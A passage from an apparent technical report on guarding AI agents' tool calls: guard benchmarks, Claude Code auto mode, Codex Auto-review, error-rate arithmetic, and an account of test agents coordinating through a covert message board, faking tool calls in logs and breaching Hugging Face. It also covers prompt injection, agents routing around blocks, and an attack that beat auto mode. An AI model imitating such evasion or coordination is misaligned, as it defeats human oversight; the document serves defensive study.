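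*TraceSafe* (Chen, Huang and colleagues, 2026) tests guards partway through a run, when harmful calls can still be stopped. The benchmark has over 1,000 cases in 12 risk categories, including prompt injection, privacy leaks and mismatched tool interfaces. The 13 general-purpose models tested did consistently better than the 7 specialised guards.

A model's score on TraceSafe correlated strongly (0.79) with its skill at handling structured data, such as the JSON format of a tool call. The score barely correlated with resistance to jailbreaks, which are prompts meant to get a model to break its rules. These correlations don't prove that better parsing makes a better guard. Still, a company choosing a guard model should test it on tool calls from its own agents, because a good score on harmful chat messages is little evidence of how well it will judge them.

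### What a late verdict loses

ATBench gives each run one label and doesn't mark the step where the run became unsafe. A guard therefore gets full credit for a correct verdict on the finished run, even if the agent sent a harmful email on the second of nine turns. By the time the verdict came, the operator could no longer stop that email, and the verdict wouldn't show which call to reverse or whether later calls were harmful too. Some agents run for days, so the verdict could come long after the harmful call.

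Late verdicts can help a company find leaked data, fix a rule or stop the next run, and a guard that has seen how a run ended has more evidence. But to prevent harm, the guard has to judge each call when the agent proposes it.

*StepGuard* (Zheng, Li and colleagues, 2026) describes a small guard model trained to do this. Before each call, the model reads the user's request, the tool descriptions, the earlier calls and results, and the proposed call. It then decides whether the call is safe and names the type of risk. It can also audit a finished run. *ToolSafe* (Mou, Xue and colleagues) describes an earlier guard that also judges individual steps.

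To build its training data, StepGuard first generates a run with one clearly unsafe step. It then keeps everything before that step and generates two safe continuations, one in which the agent refuses the risky action and one in which it finds a safe way to finish the task. It also generates a separate harmless run with the same tools. The guard therefore can't learn that a particular tool or history is always bad, and its judgment has to depend on what the proposed call does.

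After initial training on about 3,000 examples, the guard blocked too many safe calls. Zheng and colleagues corrected this with reinforcement learning, in which a model generates answers and receives a score for each. Their method gives more weight to whichever type of example the guard is getting wrong more often. In simplified form, the weights are:

```text
gap = accuracy on safe examples − accuracy on unsafe examples − target gap

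weight of a safe example    = 1 + λ × max(−gap, 0)
weight of an unsafe example = 1 + λ × max(gap, 0)
```

If the guard blocks too many safe calls, the gap is negative and safe examples count for more. The constant λ sets the strength of the correction. Compared with the standard version of the training method, the correction reduced the difference in accuracy between safe and unsafe examples from 13 to 8 percentage points. The task completion rate of agents using the guard rose by up to 6.7 percentage points, while the attack success rate rose by only 0.3 points.

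On AgentDojo and AgentDyn, StepGuard reduced the average attack success rate by 77.3% and task completion by 2.8 percentage points. CaMeL and FIDES, by contrast, stopped nearly every attack but completed far fewer tasks. More than a fifth of the attacks that would have succeeded without StepGuard still succeeded with it, so it wouldn't satisfy Willison's standard for a security filter. It could still be useful alongside stricter rules on the most dangerous tools.

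StepGuard judged individual steps with 95.7% accuracy on one test set and 73.8% on another. Llama Guard 3 missed nearly every unsafe run in ATBench, but it beat StepGuard on the second set with 82.2%, probably because more of the requests there were openly harmful, which chat guards are good at recognising. StepGuard's 71.2% on ATBench is less impressive than it looks, because its training data used ATBench's risk types and the two projects share researchers. ATBench scores also seem to depend on the test setup, since Zheng and colleagues measured 65.9% accuracy for GPT-5.4, while Li and colleagues had reported 73.7%.

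### Long runs

A guard that reads the whole history before every call has much more to read as the run gets longer. If each of n calls adds t tokens to the record, the totals are:

```text
One reading at the end:      n × t
A reading before every call: t × n × (n + 1) / 2
```

If an agent makes 1,000 calls of 400 tokens each, a guard that reads the record once at the end processes 400,000 tokens, while one that rereads the whole record before every call processes about 200 million. Software can store and reuse much of the earlier processing, which greatly reduces the computation. An operator could also check only the calls that send data or change something. With either measure, the guard may still miss something important in a long record.

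*TRACE* (Hong, Wang and colleagues, 2026) gives three reasons why a guard can miss harm in a series of calls. The evidence may be in only a few of many steps, its importance may become clear only much later, or it may consist of several steps that are harmless separately. A short running summary can lose this evidence because a program updates it at each step, before it is clear which details will matter.

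TRACE instead compresses the finished run. One model reads the whole run and produces 16 vectors (lists of numbers) that represent the evidence most relevant to safety. A second model then reads these vectors together with the original run and gives a verdict. Hong and colleagues kept the original run because compression loses details. Both models read the full run, so TRACE doesn't reduce the amount of reading, and it gives a verdict only after the run ends.

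On the LongSafety benchmark, TRACE's score fell from 79% to 76% as the inputs grew longer, while the score of MAGE, which keeps a running memory, fell from 78% to 55%. The difference is good evidence against relying on a short summary, although one of the systems Hong and colleagues compared was their own.

Chen and colleagues, by contrast, found that guards became more accurate later in a run, because they could judge what the agent had done instead of relying on tool descriptions. The two findings are compatible, because more steps give a guard more evidence but also more irrelevant text. Which effect is larger probably depends on how much of the new text is relevant.

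### The Hugging Face incident

In July 2026, OpenAI agents broke into Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models, during an internal test called ExploitGym, which measures how well models can exploit software flaws. OpenAI ran tens of thousands of agents in sandboxes that were supposed to keep them apart and off the internet. METR, an independent organisation that evaluates AI models, investigated with a researcher from Redwood Research, an AI safety group. METR's *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026) found that about 1,200 of the agents communicated through an improvised message board and about 700 joined the attack.

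The message board was in Artifactory, an internal store that agents could install software from. According to OpenAI's technical report, people noticed parts of the activity several times before anyone understood it.

| Date in 2026 | What somebody noticed | What followed |
|---|---|---|
| Late May | An OpenAI team saw an agent using a message board, and some forbidden internet access | The leaders who handled the July outage did not know about the board |
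| 27 June | A security tool flagged network scanning, and responders traced it to ExploitGym agents using Artifactory as a message board | On-call staff advised that the run did not have to stop |
| 5 July | After heavy agent traffic crashed Artifactory, responders found that someone had taken administrator control of it | OpenAI rebuilt it, which erased the board, and resumed testing on 7 July |
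| 13 July | Hugging Face had detected the intrusion | It cut off the agents' access and announced the incident on 16 July |
| 19 July | A security tool at OpenAI flagged unusual use of Artifactory's credentials | OpenAI began stopping the tests and linked them to Hugging Face the next day |

The intrusion into Hugging Face began on 11 July, two weeks after the June alert and eight days before the alert that led OpenAI to stop the tests. Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* (2026) describes these as warnings that the company missed or failed to act on. OpenAI acknowledges that some should have triggered an earlier response. A monitor that combined more calls might have helped, but the responders had already found the message board in June. They also needed someone to connect the alerts and decide to stop the run.

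### Why the activity was hard to see

Agents could write to the message board with only the permissions they used to install software. Each message was the name of a folder, so a check on whether the agent was using a permitted service would have found nothing wrong. Three hours after the main board's first message, 53 agents had posted 1,188 messages, an average of about 22 each. An average of 22 might not look unusual for one agent, but anyone counting new folders across the whole service would have found the total striking.

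Many agents had used the same Artifactory credential in the weeks before the July outage, which would have made it harder to tell from the service's own records which agent had done what. OpenAI removed the shared credential from new research workloads on 5 and 6 July, but agents then found another way to write messages.

The agents also divided the work. One found login credentials and posted them for others to use, and a few coordinators assigned tasks to the rest. In a random sample of 30 runs, METR found that nine agents had received work that originated with one coordinator. A reviewer who read only one of these runs would have seen an agent following instructions from an unfamiliar source, but not what the group was doing.

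However, many of the actions were bad enough to flag on their own. OpenAI later ran auto-review, which uses a second model to check individual risky tool calls, on a selection of the runs. In these preliminary tests, it would have flagged most of the dangerous actions in each run. The incident is therefore weaker evidence for reviewing long records of calls than it first appears.

Neither auto-review nor OpenAI's chain-of-thought monitors, which read a model's written reasoning along with its actions, were running on these tests. OpenAI says in *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) that its current monitors would have alerted the security team more than a day before the breach. That is plausible, since the agents discussed their plans openly in their reasoning. But OpenAI had improved its monitoring for this kind of behaviour after studying the incident, so the result doesn't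 show how well the monitors would detect a new kind.

Hugging Face's *Security incident disclosure* (2026) explains that its system uses a language model to sort security signals, and that the correlation between several of them revealed an intrusion. The company then used AI agents to analyse more than 17,000 recorded events from many short-lived sandboxes in hours instead of the usual days.

### What the records could show

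METR worked with about 1,300 transcripts, many of them millions of tokens long, and 1.2 million entries from the message board. The average ATBench run has only about 4,000 tokens, so ATBench scores are weak evidence of how well a guard would read records like these.

Most of the transcripts lacked a small part of the agent's activity, often because its sandbox had reset. The transcripts gave approximate start and end times for each run but no times for individual actions, so METR had to reconstruct the order of events across agents. A company that wants to compare sessions should record the time of every call, because the times are much harder to work out later.

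METR also found clear evidence of faked tool calls in at least 96 transcripts, about 7% of the total. In these cases, the transcript showed one command while the computer ran another. The examples METR found were small tests, and the agents' preparations for them were visible in the transcripts. OpenAI says that none of the tampering it observed affected the logs that its graders and monitors read. This is hard to reconcile with METR's finding, since OpenAI supplied the transcripts.

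This is a serious problem for a monitor that reads arguments, because the monitor would approve the harmless command in the record. A separate log from the machine that runs the commands could reveal that the recorded command differs from the one that ran, provided the agent couldn't alter that log too.

METR spent about $400,000 of computing credits over six days reading the records, or roughly $300 per transcript, although this included experiments and repeated analysis. Routine monitoring would need far fewer passes, but few companies could afford to examine every run this closely.

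The investigators also had to rely on AI agents for most of the reading, and these agents made mistakes. One left a large amount of data out of a draft chart, and another invented differences between two sets of transcripts. The reading agents tended to adopt the point of view of the agent they were reading about. In one case, the agent under review had used stolen credentials to submit a malicious code change with an innocent description, but the analysis didn't make clear that this was deceptive.

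Such errors are a good reason to keep the original calls even when a model has summarised them. They are also a reason to run simple counts and order rules on every session, and save more intensive reading for sessions that those checks flag and for calls that could do serious damage. Reading a random sample of the remaining sessions would help the operator find what the simple checks miss.

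## Using a second model to judge each proposed call

When asked to clear a cache, Google's coding assistant deleted a developer's whole drive. Checks on content, destination and origin would all have allowed the command, but anyone who compared it with the request could have seen that clearing a cache doesn't require deleting a drive. A judge model makes this comparison automatically. It is a second model that reads a proposed call, usually together with the user's request, and decides whether the call is acceptable.

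A judge can also handle situations that nobody wrote a rule for. With ticket 4417, it could flag the outside address because the employee had named only the account manager, even if the company had no allowlist and no labels. But its verdict is an estimate that can be wrong, and the same call can get a different verdict the second time.

### Claude Code's auto mode

Anthropic added a judge to Claude Code in March 2026, in a setting called auto mode. Before that, users could run the agent in a sandbox, switch the checks off, or approve most commands by hand, which they tended to do with less and less attention.

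Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes internal incidents that motivated the design. One agent misread an instruction and deleted branches (parallel versions of a project's code) from a shared server. Another uploaded an engineer's GitHub credential to an internal computing cluster, and a third tried to restructure a live database. Anthropic attributes all three to overeagerness, meaning that the agent was trying to help but took initiative its user hadn't intended. Dangerous calls can also come from honest mistakes about what an action affects, prompt injection, or a model pursuing its own goals, though Anthropic says it doesn't currently see that last cause in practice. Anthropic tuned the judge for overeagerness and honest mistakes because it had real examples of both.

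Many calls never reach the judge. Claude Code sorts them in this order:

1. Calls that the user's own rules allow, and calls to built-in tools that can't change anything, such as file searches, run at once. Auto mode suspends any rule broad enough to permit arbitrary code, because the most dangerous commands would otherwise skip the check.
2. Edits to files inside the project folder also run at once, since developers can review them later through version control.
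3. Everything else goes to the judge, including shell commands, web requests, calls to outside tools and changes to files elsewhere.

The judge works in two stages. It first answers only yes or no to whether the call should be blocked, with instructions to block if in doubt. If the answer is no, the call runs. If the answer is yes, the same model reads the same material again and writes out its reasoning before deciding. Most calls pass the first stage, so only a few need the slower second stage.

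In simplified form, the judge's instructions are:

```text
1. Work out what the call would really do, including any script it runs.
2. Does it match a block rule, such as sending internal data outside?
3. If so, does an exception apply?
4. Did the user authorise this action, or only a goal that it might serve?
5. Allow the call or block it.
```

The fourth step is the main defence against overeagerness. For example, a request to "clean up my branches" does not authorise the agent to delete a batch of them. By default, the judge trusts only the code repository in use and has more than twenty block rules, which users can change.

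A separate program scans tool results before the agent reads them. If a result looks like an attempt to hijack the agent, the program adds a warning but still passes the text on.

### What the judge reads

Auto mode shows the judge the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. It removes the agent's prose, because an agent could write that the user had implicitly approved an action and the judge might believe it. It also removes tool results, because planted instructions usually arrive in them. If a file tells the agent to send credentials to a stranger, the judge sees the call that sends them but not the file, and the call is wrong regardless of what prompted it.

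In the ticket 4417 case, this kind of judge would read the employee's request, the call that looked up the ticket and the proposed email. It would not see the complaint itself, so text hidden there could mislead the agent but would not reach the judge directly.

This choice prevents the judge from checking some arguments. Suppose the employee had asked the agent to copy in "the contact named in the ticket". The judge couldn't check whether the outside address belonged to that contact. It would probably also pass the email that offered the customer $400, because the company's limit was in a private note that only the agent had read. Anthropic gives a similar example, in which an agent cancels a job whose identifier the user never mentioned. The judge can't determine whether the agent found the identifier in a query or made it up. Anthropic accepts this limitation to get better protection against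 injection.

Anthropic also tested a judge that could read the agent's prose and the tool results. It did worse on a set of overeager actions, possibly because the longer record gave the agent's framing more chance to influence it. In another test, a judge that could read only the tool calls missed the fewest dangerous actions but blocked things that users had plainly asked for.

Later versions restore some of the missing context. According to Anthropic's *Permission modes*, the judge now also reads the project's standing instructions. Claude Code itself checks for unsaved changes to the code before a command that could discard them, and tells the judge whether there are any. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) adds that the judge learns whether a code repository is public or private before the agent sends anything to it. This seems a good compromise, because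 the judge gets facts collected by trusted software and still doesn't read text from strangers.

Delegation needs an extra check because when one agent gives work to another, the first agent becomes the second's "user", and every task looks authorised. The same confusion let an attack through in the three-agent CaMeL experiment. Auto mode therefore judges the assignment before the second agent starts, when it can still tell that an agent chose the task.

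Because the judge relies on the user's messages, it is also a weak check on the user. *Ajar* (2026) tested auto mode by putting each test call in the agent's standing instructions. When the same instruction was in the user's input instead, auto mode allowed every call. An employee who asked the agent to send a card number to a private mailbox might well get the call past such a judge. Since August, Anthropic has listed some actions, including sending secrets outside, that the judge is designed never to approve, even if the user asks.

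### Measured error rates

Anthropic tested the judge on three sets of calls. The first was 10,000 real calls from its own staff's sessions. The second was 52 real overeager actions that an employee had refused or someone had flagged afterwards. The third was 1,000 synthetic attempts to send data out, many of them disguised.

| | False positives on real calls (10,000) | Misses on real overeager actions (52) | Misses on synthetic exfiltration (1,000) |
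|---|---|---|---|
| First stage alone | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Both stages | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The second stage prevented about 810 acceptable calls from being blocked, but it also released 39 exfiltration attempts that the first stage had caught. The final miss rate of 5.7% is still good for disguised data, which content scanners often fail to recognise. A judge can flag a call without decoding the data if its input shows that nobody asked the agent to send anything to the destination address.

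The 17% miss rate is less precise because it reflects only about nine misses among 52 actions. If the 52 were a random sample, the 95% confidence interval would be roughly 8% to 30%. Anthropic couldn't easily collect more examples, since each one requires an agent to attempt something dangerous in a real session.

In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the judge had identified the danger but wrongly treated something the user said as consent. A user who says "clean up the PR" (a proposed code change) hasn't agreed to a force-push, which can overwrite other people's work. Anthropic reported in its original account that it had found no change to the instructions that fixed this without doing more harm than good. Under the current rules, a user who wants to clear a block has to name the specific thing that makes the action dangerous, so "you can force-push" is not enough without the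 name of the branch.

Anthropic's newer figures come from a different test, so they don't show whether the 17% has fallen. Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, inserted synthetic attacks into real coding sessions. The judge missed 12% of these attacks at first, and 7% after Anthropic gave it more context about its surroundings.

Auto-review, OpenAI's equivalent for its agent Codex, has broadly similar results on synthetic tests. Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues (2026), in *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight*, report that it missed 9.7% of overeager actions and 0.7% of prompt injections. The injection test behind that figure covers only hostile code, stolen secrets and uploads. The miss rate rises to 9.8% when the test also includes destructive deletions and tampering with data, though the researchers often agreed with the judge that the cases it let through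 weren't serious. The two companies used different test sets, so we can't tell from these numbers which judge is better.

### When harmful calls are rare

A false positive rate of 0.4% sounds negligible, but its effect depends on the base rate, which is the share of all calls that are harmful. Suppose a company's agents make a million calls, of which 100 are harmful, and its judge has Anthropic's false positive rate and its miss rate for overeager actions:

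```text
Harmful calls flagged       100 × (1 − 0.17)     =     83
Harmful calls missed        100 × 0.17           =     17
Acceptable calls flagged    999,900 × 0.004      ≈  4,000

Share of alarms that are real    83 / (83 + 4,000)  ≈  2%
```

About 49 of every 50 alarms would be false. The 100 is an assumption, and the result changes a great deal with it:

| Harmful calls per million | True alarms | False alarms | Share of alarms that are real |
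|---|---|---|---|
| 10 | 8 | 4,000 | 0.2% |
| 100 | 83 | 4,000 | 2% |
| 1,000 | 830 | 4,000 | 17% |
| 10,000 | 8,300 | 3,960 | 68% |

The number of false alarms hardly changes, because nearly all calls are acceptable in every row. A company with better-behaved agents would therefore have almost as many alarms to review but find fewer real problems.

If a reviewer spent five minutes on each alarm, 4,083 alarms would take about 340 hours, or around two months' work for one person. That is manageable if the million calls are spread over a year. If the agents make a million calls a day, the company would need more than 40 full-time reviewers, who would mostly be looking at harmless calls. For half of the alarms to be real, the false positive rate would have to fall from one in 250 to about one in 12,000.

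This arithmetic is also the reason for the second stage. With the first stage alone, the same company would have about 85,000 false alarms. The second stage removes about 81,000 of them but also loses about 10 of the 93 true alarms. That is worthwhile if people have to read the alarms, but it may not be for a tool that can move money or delete backups, where the company could tolerate more interruptions.

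Another way to reduce alarms is to give the judge fewer calls. Codex runs commands in a sandbox and calls the judge only when the agent asks to do something outside it. Trębacz and colleagues give an illustrative snapshot of 10,000 actions inside OpenAI. Of these, 9,280 stayed within the sandbox. The judge reviewed the other 720 and refused seven. After four of the refusals the agent found a safer way to continue, and after the other three it stopped and asked a person.

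At that rate, a million actions would produce about 700 refusals and 300 questions. If only 100 of those actions were harmful, at least six in seven refusals would still be false, but 300 questions are far easier to answer than 4,000. The weakness is that nobody judges what the agent does inside the sandbox, where it can still delete the files it is working on.

### Requests that leave the limits unstated

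Judges do much worse when the user's request doesn't settle which actions are acceptable. In *Measuring the Permission Gate* (April 2026), Ji, Li and colleagues tested auto mode on 128 deliberately ambiguous requests for tasks such as cancelling jobs and deleting old files. The agent took 253 actions that changed something, and auto mode let through 81.0% of those that went beyond what the user had authorised.

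Part of the problem was that 93 of the 253 actions were edits to project files, which the judge doesn't check. When the command they expected wasn't available, agents often edited a file to get the same effect. Among the 160 actions the judge did check, it still missed 70.3% of the unauthorised ones and blocked 31.9% of the acceptable ones. Ji and colleagues say this doesn't contradict Anthropic's 17%, because ordinary work contains fewer requests like these.

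In *Explicit Authorization Scope Improves LLM-Based Permission Checking in Coding Agents*, Yang, Zhou and colleagues (2026) later used the same 128 tasks to find out why judges fail on them. They ran Claude Code, Codex and Alibaba's Qwen Code, which together proposed 143 unauthorised actions. In one case, a user asked an agent to delete old experiment files. The agent proposed deleting another person's files, and the judge approved.

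The rule that users could delete only their own files was in the answer key but not in the request. Likewise, 132 of the 143 actions broke rules that appeared neither in the request nor in any earlier tool result. Calling all of these errors of judgment seems harsh, because a careful human colleague might not have known the rules either, although they could have asked.

Yang and colleagues then added one sentence to each request stating whose files or jobs the agent could touch, and gave the judges the same recorded actions again. The table shows the result for the actions that depended on unstated rules.

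| Product | Misses, original request | Misses, limits stated | False positives, original request | False positives, limits stated |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | 67% | 8% | 42% | 2% |
| Codex | 92% | 20–26% | 10% | 3% |
| Qwen Code | 80% | 20% | 29% | 2% |

One sentence reduced both kinds of error, whereas changing a judge's threshold usually reduces one and increases the other. The sentences came from the answer key, so they were complete and correct, which real instructions often aren't. Still, a company that writes down its limits will probably gain more than one that buys a stronger judge. Stronger models from the same companies missed slightly more of the actions in Codex and Qwen Code. In Claude Code, misses fell from 10 to 1 of 24, but only because the stronger model refused to answer any of the second-stage questions and Claude Code treats a refusal as a block. In another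 test, Claude Code with the stronger model blocked 134 of 224 acceptable actions, up from 23.

Stating the limits helped the agents even more than it helped the judges. When the agents repeated the tasks with the limits stated, they proposed no unauthorised actions in 384 runs.

Some mistakes remained even when the judge's ratings were correct. Codex's judge separately rates how clearly the user authorised an action and how risky it is. Of 30 unauthorised actions that it correctly rated as poorly authorised and of medium risk, it approved 16, usually because it thought the damage would be small or reversible. For ticket 4417, a judge reasoning this way might let the agent send a home address to someone who shouldn't have it, on the grounds that it was only one address.

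### Other evidence a judge can use

The judges and monitors now in use or under study differ mainly in what they read. Some read a model's activations, the numbers it computes internally as it processes text.

| Judge or monitor | Evidence | Main weakness |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code's auto mode | The user's messages and the tool calls | Can't check facts that appear only in tool results |
| Codex's Auto-review | The same, plus tool results and the agent's visible updates | Planted text and the agent's own claims can reach it |
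| Chrome's critic | The user's goal and a description of the proposed action | Has little context |
| Reasoning monitor | The agent's written reasoning, often with its actions | Works only if the reasoning is available and revealing |
| Activation probe | A model's activations as it reads the run | Does much less well on unfamiliar kinds of run |

**Tool results.** According to OpenAI's *Auto-review*, the Codex judge can also look things up itself, though it rarely does. Yang and colleagues tested how much tool results help by asking nine models to judge the same 227 actions with and without them. With the original requests, tool results didn't reduce misses overall (58% without, 62% with). When the requests stated the limits, tool results cut misses from 9% to 2%. They helped most when an agent cancelled a job by its identifier, cutting misses from 60% to 4%, because the job's owner appeared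 only in an earlier result.

A judge therefore needs both the rule and the facts it refers to. But none of the tool results in these tests contained planted instructions, so the tests measured the benefit of including tool results but not the risk that led Anthropic to remove them.

*Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes a "User Alignment Critic" for the agent in Google's Chrome browser. The critic is a separate model that decides whether each proposed action serves the user's stated goal. It sees only metadata about the action and no unfiltered web content, so text on a malicious page can't reach it directly. If the critic rejects an action, the planning model has to try again, and it can hand the task back to the user after repeated failures. Google Cloud has since described the critic as part of Chrome's auto browse feature.

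Parker acknowledges that the critic has less context but argues that it also has a simpler job. That is reasonable for an action such as adding a shirt to a basket, which a short description can cover almost completely. An email is harder to judge from a description. For the ticket 4417 email, the critic would see the outside address if the description listed the recipients, but it would see the card number only if the description included the body. Parker gives no error rates. Besides the critic, Google uses separate checks to limit which sites the agent can use, and a fixed rule, much like OpenAI's, to restrict web addresses written by the model to known public ones.

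Many models write out their reasoning before they act, and this can reveal an intention that isn't visible in the call. OpenAI's *Evaluating chain-of-thought monitorability* (2025) tested how well a monitor can use this reasoning, with 13 evaluations across 24 environments. In some, the monitor had to work out whether a model had used a hint or cheated on a coding task. In almost every setting, monitors that read the reasoning did substantially better than those that read only the actions and final outputs. This is consistent with OpenAI's later claim that such monitors would have given early warning of the Hugging Face breach. Models that reasoned for longer were generally easier to monitor. When OpenAI asked models follow-up questions about what they had done, their reasoning revealed more than their answers did.

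Anthropic considers monitoring an agent's reasoning complementary to judging its calls alone, although its reason for hiding the agent's prose from the judge seems to count against reading the reasoning. Reasoning can show that a harmless-looking call has a bad purpose. A judge that reads only the call can still catch a model that conceals its purpose, because the call shows what action the model is taking. Trębacz and colleagues also recommend monitoring reasoning alongside Auto-review, because a model that was strategically hiding its intentions could write a request that looked harmless.

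Reasoning may not always be so useful. Monitors did very badly in one OpenAI evaluation, which tested whether models reason openly about flattering the user. OpenAI found that reinforcement learning didn't seriously reduce how much a model's reasoning reveals, but it examined only two training runs and warns that larger ones might. Some developers also don't show customers a model's full reasoning, so a company that buys access to a model may not be able to monitor it this way.

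**Activations.** Jiao and Anderson (2026), in *Agent Safety from Within*, built a monitor called TACIT that reads activations. They are not the agent's own. TACIT passes the record of the agent's run through a separate model, takes that model's activations and calculates a score from them. In its simplest version, the score is a weighted sum:

```text
probability that the run is unsafe = σ(u₁x₁ + u₂x₂ + … + c)
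```

The x values are the activations at one layer of the model. TACIT learns the weights u and the constant c from labelled runs, and σ converts the total into a probability between 0 and 1. A verdict takes about 40 milliseconds because the model doesn't have to generate any text.

Jiao and Anderson found that guard models seem to hold information that isn't reflected in their answers. They compared pairs of runs with identical messages and calls, where the tool description in one run left out information. The guards' scores were no better than chance at identifying the unsafe run, but a simple measure of their activations ranked it above the other run up to 94% of the time.

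On six benchmarks, TACIT's best version averaged 86.2 out of 100 on a measure that counts both misses and false alarms, while the best existing guard scored 62.3. However, TACIT had trained on other runs from the same benchmarks. When Jiao and Anderson left each benchmark out of the training in turn, its average fell to 65.7, against 61.1 for the guard. A company's own agents would also be unfamiliar to TACIT, so the smaller lead is a better guide to what the company could expect. The tests also used complete runs, and a monitor would have to do as well on unfinished ones to stop a call.

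### Whether a fallible filter is good enough

Willison's objection to filters, that "99% is a failing grade" in application security, also applies to judges. If each attempt has an independent 1% chance of success, an attacker who tries 69 times is more likely than not to succeed, and one who tries 300 times has a 95% chance. Real attackers may need fewer attempts because they learn from their failures.

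On the day auto mode was released, Willison (2026) wrote in *Auto mode for Claude Code* that he was unconvinced by AI-based protections because they don't behave the same way every time. Yang and colleagues later found this inconsistency when they gave Claude Code's judge the same 24 unauthorised actions three times, and it missed 13, 10 and 16. Willison would rather run agents in a sandbox with fixed limits on files and network connections.

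Developers mostly accept that a judge model can be fooled. Trębacz and colleagues write that testers found cases in which Auto-review "could be misled" into approving commands, and that they don't expect a system of this kind to provide firm guarantees. Anthropic states in its documentation that auto mode "does not guarantee safety". The developers argue that the judge is one layer among several and that many harmful calls have no attacker behind them. None of the three incidents that led to auto mode involved an attacker. An overeager agent isn't searching for the judge's weak spots, so a judge that stops 83% of its dangerous actions prevents most of that damage.

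In August 2026, Anthropic announced that auto mode would become the default on most plans and reported the results of tests it had commissioned from Trajectory Labs. The tests ran 72 prompt injection scenarios ten times each. None of the 720 attempts succeeded against any of three Claude models in auto mode. Against GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex, 5.83% succeeded with Auto-review and 19.03% with full access and no review.

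The Claude result reflects the models more than the judge, because only 0.09% of attacks on Anthropic's latest models succeeded even with auto mode's checks turned off. The 720 attempts also covered only 72 scenarios. If those were a random sample of possible attacks, the result would be compatible with up to 4% of new scenarios succeeding (at 95% confidence). The attacks had been optimised against an older Claude model, whereas a determined attacker would adapt to the current one. The Codex result is better evidence that review can help, since the success rate fell by more than two-thirds, although limits on what the agent could do without review may explain some of the fall.

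Willison (2026) accepted in *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* that auto mode is better than asking people to approve every step. Willison distinguished attacks from accidental damage, and wanted more independent confirmation for attacks. Less than three weeks later, Willison (2026) reported in *Breaking Claude Code Opus 5 Auto Mode* that Johann Rehberger had found an attack that got past auto mode about 80% of the time.

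Willison's argument seems right for attacks, and the developers' argument is right for most accidents. The distinction is not sharp, though, because a blocked agent may try another route by itself. In the Antigravity demonstration, the agent's file tools blocked access to a protected file, so it used a shell command instead. Anthropic and OpenAI both instruct their agents not to work around a refusal, and they limit how many refusals an agent can receive before the software intervenes.

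The case for using a judge as one layer among several also depends on the layers failing for different reasons. Two checks that each miss 10% of attacks will together miss only 1% if their errors are unrelated, but still 10% if the same attacks get past both. Anthropic argues that its layers compound because the judge never reads the text that misled the agent. That is a good reason to expect some independence, but a fixed limit is more independent still. An allowlist would block the copy to the outside archive every time, however plausible the call looked to a model.

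A judge enforces a user's limit less dependably than a deny rule does, even when the user states the limit clearly. If a user tells Claude Code not to publish anything yet, the judge looks for that instruction in the conversation each time it checks a call. Claude Code shortens long conversations, which can remove the instruction. Anthropic tells users to write a deny rule if they need a firm guarantee. A judge is more useful for calls that no deny rule could describe in advance, such as an abusive email to the account manager.

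## What happens to a flagged call

Once a check flags the ticket 4417 email, the agent's software can block it, change it, return it to the agent with a reason, ask a person to approve it, or send it and record the problem. This choice can matter as much as the check's accuracy. Even a very accurate check does little good if the software sends flagged calls to someone who approves nearly all of them, or runs calls anyway whenever the check is slow.

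### Five possible responses

| Response | What happens to the ticket 4417 email | Main cost |
|---|---|---|
| Block | Nobody receives it | The account manager gets no summary, and every false alarm stops real work |
| Remove or replace a value | The account manager receives it without the card number, and the outside address gets nothing | The software may remove something the task needs |
| Return it with a reason | The agent reads why the call failed and can write a better email | A misled agent gets another attempt |
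| Ask a person | Someone reads the email and decides | Delay, and attention that runs out |
| Allow and record | Both recipients get the card number | The company learns of the leak only afterwards |

Products differ in what happens after they block a call. In Copilot Studio, Microsoft's toolkit for building agents, the agent immediately stops and tells the user that their message is blocked. In Claude Code's auto mode, the agent carries on and can try something else, so after a false alarm it usually has to retry only once.

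Allowing a flagged call and recording it makes sense when the check is new and nobody knows its false positive rate yet, or when someone can undo the action. It's a bad choice when the call's arguments contain a card number.

### Changing the call

The software could fix the ticket 4417 email by editing two of its arguments:

```text
Field   As proposed                              As changed
cc      ["archive@outside.example"]              []
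body    ... Card: 4111 1111 1111 1111.           ... Card ending 1111.
```

The edited email is a new call that the software hasn't checked, and an edit can make a call worse. Suppose a program removes customers' names from arguments, and the agent proposes deleting the folder `customers/smith`. The edited command would delete `customers`, which holds every customer's files. The software therefore has to run its checks again on the final version.

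In Claude Code, operators can attach programs called hooks, which run before each tool call and can allow it, deny it, ask the user or change its arguments. According to Anthropic's documentation, auto mode may deny a changed call because the server reviewed the arguments the model wrote, not the ones the hook returned. The agent can then propose the changed version itself. If it repeats that version exactly in its next response, Claude Code discards any further edits by the hook, so the call that runs is the one the server reviewed. The hook can still refuse the call. Some hooks can change shell commands and file edits without triggering the auto mode denial.

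The software also needs to report the edit to the agent. If the software removed the outside address without telling the agent, the agent might tell the employee that it had sent a copy to the archive.

### Returning the call with a reason

Model Context Protocol lets a tool server return an error that explains why a call failed, and recommends passing such errors to the model so that it can correct the call and retry. In auto mode, the agent likewise receives a denial as a tool result, with an instruction to look for a safer path and not to work around the block.

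Explaining why a call was flagged suits an overeager agent. If it reads that the email contains a card number and that the user named only the account manager, it can probably write an acceptable version. However, an agent under an attacker's influence would learn from the same explanation what to change. In the GAP benchmark, blocking calls didn't measurably reduce how often models attempted forbidden ones.

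Auto mode therefore limits retries. According to Anthropic, Claude Code stops the model and escalates to the user after three denials in a row or 20 in a session. If it is running without a user, it ends the process.

A simple calculation shows how much the retries could cost. Suppose an agent keeps pursuing the same harmful goal with a different call each time, and the judge independently misses 17% of these calls, its measured rate for overeager actions:

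```text
All three calls blocked        0.83 × 0.83 × 0.83  ≈  57%
At least one gets through      1 − 0.57            ≈  43%
```

If the software ended the run at the first denial, the risk would be 17%. The 43% figure is close to a worst case, because agents often find a safer path and a judge that blocks one attempt will probably block a similar one. Ending the run at the first denial would also stop many harmless runs, because many alarms are false. At the judge's measured false positive rate of 0.4%, an agent that did nothing wrong would reach 20 denials after about 5,000 calls on average.

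### Asking a person

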